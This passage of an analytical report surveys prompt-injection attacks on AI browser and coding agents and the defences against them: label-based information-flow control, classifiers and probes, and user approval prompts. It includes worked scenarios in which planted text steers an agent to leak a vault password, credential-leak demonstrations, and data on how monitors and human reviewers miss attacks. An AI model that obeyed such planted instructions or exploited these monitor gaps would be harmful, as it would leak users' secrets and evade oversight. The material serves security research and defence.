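- **A harmless transfer between sites.** The user wanted to check whether a discounted speaker was really cheaper than usual. The agent had to copy the product's name from a deals site to a shopping search engine. SOPGuard asked for approval in all 25 runs, while SPIDES completed 21 of them without asking.

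The same site held the private recovery address and the public profile. The speaker's name was public on both sites. An origin identifies the site that holds the data, but not who is allowed to read it.

### Two labels and a rule for sending

SPIDES uses information-flow control, which labels data and blocks actions that would violate the labels' restrictions. Each part of a page has two labels. The integrity label is "trusted" if the site's operator vouches for the text, and "untrusted" if, for example, a customer wrote it. The confidentiality label is the set of permitted readers, which can include the user and particular origins. For example, everyone might be allowed to read a product name, but only the user and the shop could read an address in the user's account.

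The site's operator writes these labels into the page's code, because only the operator knows which text came from customers and which data is private. The user keeps a list of sites whose operators they trust to do this. SPIDES ignores labels on all other sites and treats everything there as untrusted and public. This design relies on the user having accounts only on trusted sites, so the others should have nothing private to protect.

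SPIDES at first hides untrusted or private text from the model by replacing it with a placeholder. The agent can copy the placeholder into a form without knowing its contents, or pass it to a second model that has no tools. That second model can summarise an email full of planted text, but it cannot open a web address, and SPIDES keeps its summary behind another placeholder until showing it to the user.

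If the agent needs to read the hidden text to decide what to do, it can reveal it, but SPIDES then adds the text's labels to the agent's whole context. Once the agent has read anything untrusted, SPIDES treats everything it does afterwards as influenced by untrusted text. Once it has read a private value, only that value's permitted readers can receive what it writes later. The context's labels can become stricter during a task but can't be loosened.

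Before each action, SPIDES checks the labels of the agent's context and of any data the action contains. The table lists the conditions under which the agent can proceed without asking the user.

| Action | Condition |
|---|---|
| Reading the current page | None |
| Filling in a field without submitting it, on any site | No untrusted influence, or the site is a permitted reader |
| Opening an address, clicking or submitting on an untrusted site | No untrusted influence, or the site is a permitted reader |
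| Opening an address, clicking or submitting on a trusted site | No untrusted influence |
| Running code in the page | Always blocked |

The rule is stricter for trusted sites because the user may be signed in there, and a click could buy something or delete an account.

### A password vault with labels

Suppose Ana's calendar and her password manager, vault.example, both label their pages and are on her trusted list. She asks the agent to handle a meeting invitation like the one in the 1Password case.

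1. The agent opens the calendar. The organiser's text is untrusted, so the agent receives a placeholder.
2. It cannot handle the invitation without reading the details, so it reveals them. Its context is now untrusted.
3. The planted text tells it to open vault.example. This is a trusted site, and untrusted text has influenced the agent, so SPIDES asks Ana first. If she refuses, the attack ends before the agent sees the vault.
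4. Suppose she approves. The password's permitted readers are {Ana, vault.example}.
5. The agent tries to open notes.example with the password in the query string. Untrusted text has influenced it, and notes.example is not a permitted reader. Neither condition holds, so the browser sends nothing unless Ana approves again.

Encoding the password would not help the attacker, as with OpenAI's address index. SPIDES' rule also covers leaks through the choice of a fixed address. Once the agent has read both the planted text and the password, it needs Ana's approval to open even an address at notes.example that contains nothing about her.

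If the agent had read only trusted text and Ana asked it to copy a password from the vault into a new site, SPIDES would send the password without prompting her. Zverev and colleagues allow this because no attacker could have influenced the decision. This avoids many unnecessary prompts, but SPIDES might not stop a model from mistakenly sending a password to the wrong site. It also wouldn't stop the leak in Shahriar and colleagues' library example if the library were on the trusted list, since nobody had planted any text there.

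### Results on 28 websites

Zverev and colleagues built 28 linked websites with 470 pages and labelled them all. They wrote 56 ordinary tasks, 22 of which needed data to move between sites, and 56 attacks. Half the attacks were designed to take private data, and half to make the agent do something harmful, such as place an order.

If the model received instructions planted by an attacker, the researchers replaced its next actions with the ones the attacker wanted, so the test did not depend on how well an attacker writes. Six attacks planted false data instead of instructions, and in those the researchers let the model respond by itself. The table combines their results for the different kinds of task and attack, averaged over five repetitions.

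| Model | Tasks completed, no defence | Tasks completed, SPIDES | Attacks succeeded, no defence | Attacks succeeded, SOPGuard | Attacks succeeded, SPIDES |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-5.6 Sol | 91.1% | 86.1% | 95.7% | 57.9% | 0% |
| GPT-5.6 Terra | 88.2% | 77.1% | 95.0% | 58.2% | 0% |
| Claude Opus 5.5 | 58.2% | 67.1% | 57.5% | 53.2% | 0% |
| Claude Opus 5 | 68.9% | 69.3% | 71.8% | 65.7% | 0% |
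| Claude Sonnet 5 | 88.9% | 82.1% | 92.5% | 73.2% | 0% |

SPIDES lowered the task completion rates of three models by 5 to 11 percentage points. The two Claude Opus models completed more tasks with it, one slightly more and the other considerably more. Without SPIDES, Anthropic's safety filters sometimes blocked tasks that included login details or phishing messages. Replacing the login details with placeholders prevented some of those blocks.

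The comparison with SOPGuard is somewhat unfair. SOPGuard tries to stop data from crossing between sites, but 26 of the 56 attacks stayed within one site and half were not attempts to steal data. Its failures mostly show how many attacks fall outside the same-origin policy. Untrusted Content Masking, which hides untrusted text from the model but does not track private data, was a closer competitor to SPIDES. Attacks succeeded against it in 4.6% to 6.8% of cases, and it completed fewer tasks than SPIDES with every model.

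The zero for SPIDES depends on correct labels and on a simulated user who approved every legitimate request and refused every one that an attacker had influenced. SPIDES asked for approval an average of 1.84 times per completed task, compared with 0.22 for SOPGuard, so it gives a real user more chances to make a mistake. It also roughly doubled the estimated cost of running the models, to between $0.37 and $1.42 per task. It works only with agents that read a page as text, and some browser agents also use screenshots.

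### Who will label the web

SPIDES needs websites to add labels to their pages, which they have not done yet. Zverev and colleagues compare these labels to the descriptions that many sites already add for people who use screen readers. One label can cover a whole section of a page, so operators do not have to label every element separately.

Labelling mistakes would be serious, however, because SPIDES treats unlabelled content on a trusted site as both trusted and public. That default lets unlabelled sites keep working, but it means a missing label can help an attacker. Suppose Ana's mailbox contains planted text and a one-time code. If her email provider forgets to label the code as private, any site is allowed to read it, and the agent can send it to notes.example without asking. If the provider instead forgets to label the planted text as untrusted, the agent can send the code even though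 the code is correctly labelled. The rule for sending requires only one of its two conditions to be met, so one missing label, on either the code or the planted text, can be enough to allow a leak.

Iqbal (2026) argues in *What It Is, Not What It Says* that site owners could not label everything. Advertising and analytics companies supply scripts that add text and buttons to a page after it loads, and the owner often doesn't know what they will add. Iqbal recorded which script created or changed each element on 1,270 real webpages. When a third party had added or altered an element, the browser attributed it to the site itself in 58.7% of cases.

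This weakens Google's design as well as SPIDES. Chrome can hide an advertisement that sits in a frame from another origin, but text that an advertiser's script writes directly into the page has the site's own origin. The site's owner could label the page's advertising space as untrusted, but that would help only if the script stayed inside it. Iqbal also cites a test of Untrusted Content Masking in which a single wrong label raised the attackers' success rate from 0% to 6%.

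Software could instead work out the labels. *Prismata* (2026) describes prompt injection on an otherwise harmless site as "cross-site prompting", by analogy with cross-site scripting, and uses a model to infer who wrote each part of a page. Sites would not have to do anything, but Iqbal objects that the labels would again depend on a model's judgement.

Iqbal's system, INTACT, uses information from the browser to trace each page element to the script that made it. It then shows the model one element at a time, so that text in an advertisement cannot influence what the agent does with the login button. It asks the user before the agent acts on anything from a third party. In tests on 1,091 real pages with planted attacks, 12.8% of attacks got through INTACT's planning stage, compared with 73.1% for an ordinary agent. The attacks that got through INTACT's planning stage could at most produce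 a request for the user's approval. Showing the model one element at a time disrupted 3.7% of tasks.

INTACT needs no labels from site owners, but it treats everything the site itself delivers as trusted and looks for outside text only in what third parties add. It covers attacks within a single page, whereas the attack on 1Password moved across three sites.

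## 2026: how often models and people refuse

If a model always ignored planted text, most of these labels and checks would be unnecessary, so websites would not have to label their pages and Ana would not have to answer prompts. If she asked her agent to handle a meeting invitation, it would read the organiser's text, recognise that the task didn't require opening her password vault, and carry on. It would also refuse to leak a password by any route, including posting it in a comment, which a rule about web addresses would not prevent.

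The evidence for relying on better models grew stronger in 2026. OpenAI credits safety training for ChatGPT's refusal of most known attacks, so Safe Url has to handle only the rest. Known attacks exclude any that nobody noticed. OpenAI also expects a maximally intelligent model to resist deception better than a human employee, but says using one will not always be practical or worth the cost.

### No successes in 720 attempts

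The most impressive result comes from Claude Code, Anthropic's programming agent. *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (Anthropic, 2026) describes a test Anthropic commissioned from an outside company, Trajectory Labs. In auto mode, a classifier reviews each action and blocks dangerous ones, so the agent rarely has to ask the user. Other software, which Anthropic calls probes, looks for planted instructions in web pages and files the agent reads.

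Trajectory Labs wrote 72 scenarios in which a successful attack would cause serious harm, such as sending out sensitive data or phishing for credentials. It ran each scenario ten times, for 720 attempts in total.

| Models and setting | Attacks that succeeded |
|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 and Sonnet 5 in auto mode | 0% |
| Anthropic's latest models with no extra safeguards | 0.09% on average |
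| GPT-5.6 Sol in OpenAI's Codex, with automatic review | 5.83% |
| GPT-5.6 Sol in Codex, with full access | 19.03% |

If the 0.09% covers the same three Claude models, it amounts to about two successes in 2,160 attempts. The models' own refusals therefore stopped nearly all the attacks, leaving auto mode almost none to stop. The classifier is less reliable on its own. When Apollo Research, an AI safety company, inserted artificial attacks into records of real coding sessions, the classifier missed 12% of them, and 7% after Anthropic improved it.

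Trajectory Labs kept the scenarios from Anthropic, so Anthropic could not have trained its models on them. Trajectory Labs developed the attacks against an older model, Claude Opus 4.7, and did not adapt them to the newer ones. OpenAI released a new version of its automatic review shortly before Anthropic published the results, so the figure for Codex may be out of date.

Zero successes is also compatible with a small real success rate. If each attempt independently had a 0.4% chance of success, 720 attempts would still produce no successes about one time in twenty. But repeated runs of the same scenario tend to have the same outcome. If all ten runs of each scenario always did, the test would amount to only 72 independent attempts, and the corresponding rate would be about 4%.

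Willison hoped that Anthropic had solved the problem but wanted more independent confirmation. It was hard to see how an automatic check could recognise a routine-looking setup instruction that installed malicious software.

### What the developers publish about browsers

The Claude Code test included browser tasks, using a simple connection to Chrome that Trajectory Labs built. This connection did not include the safeguards in Anthropic's and OpenAI's own browser extensions, so the test does not measure how well those products resist attack.

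Anthropic publishes more about browser agents than its competitors do. The technology news site VentureBeat compared the developers' safety documents after Anthropic released Claude Opus 4.8 in May 2026. Anthropic had tested that model's resistance to prompt injection in 129 browser environments. OpenAI's document for GPT-5.5 had one score, for known attacks through connectors, which link a model to other services. Google's documents for Gemini 3 had no prompt injection results.

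Anthropic's browser figures come from tests that gave attackers different opportunities. In late 2025, Anthropic tested Claude for Chrome against an automated attacker that combined techniques known to work and made up to 100 attempts in each environment. The later figures come from system cards, in which developers report their tests of new models.

| Model | What the attacker could do | Result |
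|---|---|---|
| Claude Opus 4.5 | Adapt its attacks, with 100 attempts in each environment | 8.0% success against the model alone, 1.4% with improved safeguards |
| Claude Opus 5 | Attack the agent in 129 scenarios in Anthropic's own software | 0% success |
| Claude Fable 5.1 | Reuse attacks developed against Opus 4.7 | At least as resistant as Fable 5, but some attacks still worked without extra safeguards |

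The zero comes from Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Opus 5. The Decoder, an AI news site, called the figure "a big deal" and also noted that OpenAI had admitted the previous December that prompt injection might never be fully solved.

The safeguards seem to matter more for browser agents than in the Claude Code test. VentureBeat's headline gives a rate of 31% for attacks on Anthropic's browser agent before its safeguards engaged. Anthropic's software can add probes and other checks, but a company that builds a browser on the same model may not have them.

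OpenAI and Google have not published comparable figures, so outsiders cannot check whether refusals protect Atlas or Chrome as well as they protect Claude for Chrome. OpenAI says most attacks fail but gives no rate for Atlas. Either company may run such tests without publishing the results, and the lack of figures does not mean that their browser agents are less safe.

### Attackers who adapt

Tests with a fixed set of attacks can greatly underestimate the risk. *The Attacker Moves Second* (Nasr and colleagues, 2025) examined 12 published defences against prompt injection and jailbreaking. The developers of most of these defences had reported attack success rates near zero. Nasr and colleagues, who included researchers from OpenAI, Anthropic and Google DeepMind, adapted their attacks to each defence with automated search, reinforcement learning and human testers. More than 90% of their attacks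 succeeded against most of the defences.

A developer has to choose a defence first, and an attacker can then keep trying until something gets past it. The study predates the models of 2026, so its 90% figure is not an estimate of how often they would fail. But it shows that a defence's near-zero failure rate against old attacks is a poor guide to how it will handle new ones.

Anthropic's *System Card* (2026) for Claude Fable 5.1 cites the study and reports a harder test of the company's models in coding tasks. The security company Gray Swan trained an automated attacker against earlier Claude models on 40 scenarios, then ran it against newer models on the same scenarios, with 200 attempts at each. The table gives results for models that reason before they answer.

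| Model | Successful attempts without probes | Scenarios with at least one success | Successful attempts with probes | Scenarios with at least one success |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5.1 | 9.26% | 31 of 40 | 2.05% | 18 of 40 |
| Claude Opus 5 | 2.68% | 27 of 40 | 0.39% | 11 of 40 |
| Claude Sonnet 5 | 0.3% | 7 of 40 | 0.09% | 5 of 40 |

These conditions were chosen to favour the attacker. A real attacker usually doesn't know exactly how the target's agent works, and 200 attempts on one person could attract attention. The results are still far from zero, and they cover some of the same models as the Trajectory Labs test.

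Fable 5.1 was the most capable model but also the least resistant. With probes on, attacks succeeded against it more than twenty times as often as against Sonnet 5. On a different Gray Swan benchmark, which uses fixed attacks from public competitions, Fable 5.1 was the most resistant model tested. Given 15 attempts, attackers succeeded 1.0% of the time against Fable 5.1, 4.8% against Opus 5 and 9.2% against Google's Gemini 3.7 Flash. Most other developers' models had rates between 24% and 53%.

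A more capable model does not automatically resist attacks better, and which model resists best depends on the attacker. Developers have to train models specifically to resist attacks, as Anthropic and OpenAI do, and retest them when attackers change their methods.

In late August 2026, less than three weeks after Anthropic published the 720 attempts, Rehberger found a way past auto mode. Willison (2026), in *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode*, reported that the attack worked 80% of the time, according to Rehberger, who had also found the early leaks from Bing Chat and ChatGPT. The attack was specific to a coding agent, but nothing in the earlier test had suggested that auto mode was vulnerable to such an attack.

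### BioShocking

In June 2026, LayerX published BioShocking, a demonstration on six AI browsers and assistants. The user was signed in to GitHub and asked the agent to complete a task on a page that LayerX controlled. All six agents copied an SSH credential from the user's work repository and sent it to the attacker. *Researchers Trick AI Browsers Into Leaking Credentials* (Mascellino, 2026) notes that none of the six identified this as something it should refuse.

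LayerX had reported the problem to the companies months earlier, and lists these outcomes:

| Product | Date of report | Outcome according to LayerX |
|---|---|---|
| Comet | 20 October 2025 | Perplexity closed the report without acting on it |
| ChatGPT Atlas | 30 October 2025 | OpenAI fixed the problem |
| Fellou | 30 October 2025 | No response |
| Genspark Browser | 30 October 2025 | No response |
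| Sigma Browser | 30 October 2025 | No response |
| Claude for Chrome | 26 January 2026 | Anthropic's patch failed |

The credential was harmless text in a test file. LayerX did not report how many times it tried the attack on each product, so the success rate is unknown. It told all six companies about the problem by late January 2026, about six months before Anthropic released Opus 5, and the newer model might refuse the same instructions. BioShocking therefore does not contradict the zero in Anthropic's browser test.

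Products from very different companies had the same weakness. Sigma Browser users gain nothing from a better model until Sigma's makers adopt it, and three of the six companies did not respond to a report that their product leaked credentials. Figures for the leading developers' newest models are therefore weak evidence of how well most users of AI browsers are protected.

LayerX recommends that a browser ask the user before its agent reads data in a signed-in account. The Hacker News repeats the suggestion that one such question would have stopped the attack. This is probably right if the user reads the question and considers why the task would need a GitHub repository.

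### A small chance repeated many times

If each attempt has a 1% chance of making Ana's agent leak a credential, the chance that 100 independent attempts all fail is 0.99¹⁰⁰, or about 37%. The chance that at least one succeeds is about 63%. In general, if one attempt succeeds with probability *p*, at least one of *n* independent attempts succeeds with probability 1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ.

| Chance per attempt | 10 attempts | 100 attempts | 1,000 attempts |
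|---|---|---|---|
| 5% | 40% | 99% | Over 99.9% |
| 1% | 10% | 63% | Over 99.9% |
| 0.1% | 1% | 10% | 63% |
| 0.01% | 0.1% | 1% | 10% |

If a model is ten times as resistant, an attacker needs about ten times as many attempts. This helps, but an email costs almost nothing to send, and a comment on a popular page can reach many agents at once.

An attacker can also spread the attempts across different people. Anthropic points out that one email can go to a thousand inboxes. At an average success rate of 1%, the attacker can expect ten leaks. That may be enough for an attacker who wants any usable account, but one who wants Ana's has to keep trying.

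This is the reasoning behind Willison's view that stopping 99% of attacks is a failing grade in security. The best counterargument is that criminals can very cheaply buy everything an infostealer took from one computer, so many will not bother with an attack that usually fails. A very low success rate could therefore make agent leaks rare, though still possible. This argument is weaker for a company with valuable accounts, because an attacker may spend weeks developing an attack against it.

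### When attempts are not independent

The 63% figure holds only if a failed attack doesn't change the next one's chance of success. But a model that resists one attack in a given situation will often resist similar ones, so repeated attempts succeed less often than the formula predicts.

The Decoder's *Claude Opus 4.5 resists prompt injections better than rivals* reports that in an earlier Gray Swan benchmark, a strong attack succeeded 4.7% of the time with one attempt, 33.6% with ten and 63% with 100. If the attempts had been independent, the rates for ten and 100 attempts would have been about 38% and 99%.

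The difference is larger in the coding test of Fable 5.1. With probes on, 2.05% of attempts succeeded. If every attempt had independently had that chance, 200 attempts per scenario would have produced at least one success in about 39 of the 40 scenarios. The attacker succeeded in only 18, because the successes were concentrated in scenarios where the model was weak.

Attempts can also depend on each other because an attacker who sees why one failed can improve the next. The chance of success then rises over time, as in Nasr and colleagues' tests. It falls if a company notices the attempts and blocks the sender or adds the attack to its training data.

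Whether attacks succeed independently of each other also matters when many people use the same model. An average success rate of 1% could mean that each email sent to a thousand people causes about ten leaks, or that 99 emails in a hundred fail on everyone and the other works on nearly all thousand agents. In the second case, an attacker who finds the right text can steal from many people before the developer responds.

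Anthropic notes that an attack has to get past both the probes, which check incoming text, and the classifier, which checks outgoing actions. If each missed 10% of attacks independently, only 1% would get past both. But text that resembles an ordinary request could mislead both at once, in which case more than 1% would get through.

### How far coding results apply to browsing

How well an agent resists attacks while coding is a poor guide to how well it resists them when operating a graphical interface. VentureBeat reported in February 2026 that Claude Opus 4.6 resisted all 200 attack attempts in a restricted coding environment. When it operated a graphical interface without safeguards, the first attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time, and by the 200th attempt the attacker had succeeded in 78.6% of cases. With safeguards, the success rate by the 200th attempt was 57.1%.

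Newer models have the same weakness to a smaller degree. On Gray Swan's benchmark of fixed attacks, attackers with 15 attempts succeeded against Fable 5.1 in 0.3% of cases in coding and 4.1% in operating a computer through its screen. The coding figure partly reflects the older Opus 4.8, because a separate safety filter passed the request to that model in about half of the coding runs. In the Trajectory Labs test, OpenAI's models were also more vulnerable on browser tasks.

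But attacks don't always succeed more often in browsing than in coding. Opus 5 had no failures in Anthropic's browser test, while Gray Swan's trained attacker succeeded at least once in 27 of the 40 coding scenarios when the probes were off. The coding attacker probably had more opportunity to learn the model's weaknesses. Such rates are comparable only if the attackers had similar knowledge and made a similar number of attempts.

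Auto mode also relies on information that a browser may not have. Before Claude Code sends out a user's code, the classifier checks whether the destination is public, private or trusted, and it can recognise many dangerous commands by what they do. A browser agent can leak a password by opening a page, which is a routine part of its legitimate work, and the software may not be able to determine who controls the destination.

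The models' own refusals are more likely to carry over, since the Claude models resisted nearly every attack in the Trajectory Labs test, including those in browser tasks, even without auto mode. Anthropic describes its figures as specific to Claude Code, but in October 2026 it announced that auto mode would become the default in most Claude apps. That change will make separate figures for each app more important.

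Refusal rates do not measure attacks that bypass the model's judgement. *AI agent security* (Constantin, 2026) describes a demonstration by Manifold Security in which another browser extension got Claude for Chrome to read the user's Gmail, documents and calendar. The extension started one of Claude's built-in tasks, so refusing every planted instruction would not have prevented the attack. Manifold rated the flaw critical if the user had let Claude act without asking.

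### How often people refuse

Many defences against agent leaks eventually ask the user. Safe Url can show a warning, and 1Password can ask before filling in a login. SPIDES had no successful attacks in tests, but the simulated user in those tests never approved a bad request. Anthropic's study of human approval suggests that real users make many mistakes.

Anthropic used a research company to recruit 1,053 paid professional testers for a coding study. The testers knew they were taking part in an evaluation, but not what it measured. During each session, the software replaced the text of one permission prompt with a clearly dangerous command. Approving the command had no harmful effect. Of the testers, 143, or 13.6%, refused it. Auto mode's classifier blocked 937 of the same commands, or 89%.

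Anthropic also reports how many commands only the person or only the classifier stopped, which is enough to work out the remaining numbers:

| | Classifier blocked | Classifier allowed |
|---|---|---|
| Tester refused | 137 | 6 |
| Tester approved | 800 | 110 |

Requiring approval from both the classifier and the testers would have stopped 943 dangerous commands, only six more than the classifier alone. More than one dangerous command in ten would still have gotten through.

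Testers also refused fewer of the dangerous commands as a session went on, from about 17% early in the session to about 5% after 50 or more prompts. The classifier's rate stayed the same.

People would probably do somewhat better with their own accounts than they did in the study. The testers worked in a special environment with none of their own data at risk, and some may have assumed that nothing in a study could do real damage. Anthropic also had a commercial reason to show that auto mode was safer, because auto mode lets the agent work longer without interruption. But these factors are unlikely to explain all of such a large gap, and Willison agrees that automatic checks are better than constant requests for approval.

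Anthropic's records of ordinary use are harder to interpret. Claude Code users approve 97% of permission prompts, but most prompts concern safe actions, so a careful reviewer would also approve nearly all of them. Users reject 39% of the plans Claude submits for approval before starting work. Some of those rejections must be about quality rather than danger, but they suggest that people think about a question when it is infrequent and they understand what depends on it.

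The study did not test browser prompts, which may be easier to judge than a programmer's command. Ana can decide without technical knowledge whether her agent may send her bank password to notes.example. She would find it harder to judge a request to open a long, unfamiliar address, especially after approving twenty similar ones that morning. Prompts work best if the browser reserves them for unusual actions and shows both the data and its destination.

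Auto mode follows part of this advice. The classifier blocks most dangerous actions without asking the user, and Claude then looks for a safer way to proceed. Claude Code returns to manual approval only after three blocks in a row or twenty in a session. Anthropic designed the classifier never to approve sending secrets outside, so the user has to leave auto mode or run the command personally, which makes it harder to approve a leak by reflex.

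### Demonstrations and real thefts

Researchers demonstrated the browser attacks in this history, from the Reddit comment to the 1Password vault and BioShocking. The demonstrations show that the products would leak a credential under the researchers' conditions, but not that criminals have used the same methods. Perplexity said nobody had exploited CometJacking, and Reddy and Gujral found no evidence that anyone had used EchoLeak against customers.

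Public records can blur this difference. The OECD's *BioShocking Exploit Exposes Major Security Flaws in AI Browsers* (2026), an entry in its AI incident monitor, includes an AI-generated explanation that calls the harm "direct and realized", but LayerX had taken only a harmless test file. The entry also credits the technique to both LayerX and the University of Washington, while LayerX's account mentions only its own researchers. Anyone who counts such entries as thefts will overestimate how often criminals steal credentials this way.

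Willison told the Economist in September 2025 that nobody had yet stolen millions of dollars through prompt injection, but expected something expensive to happen eventually. In August 2026, Willison was still predicting a major disaster involving coding agents for that year, and hoped to be wrong. These are one well-informed observer's impressions, and because they concern large disasters, they do not rule out smaller thefts.

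A small theft could easily go unrecognised. If a criminal used Ana's API key, she might blame an infostealer or her own carelessness. To confirm that her agent had leaked the key, an investigator would need the planted text and a record of what the agent did after reading it. By then, Ana may have deleted the email.
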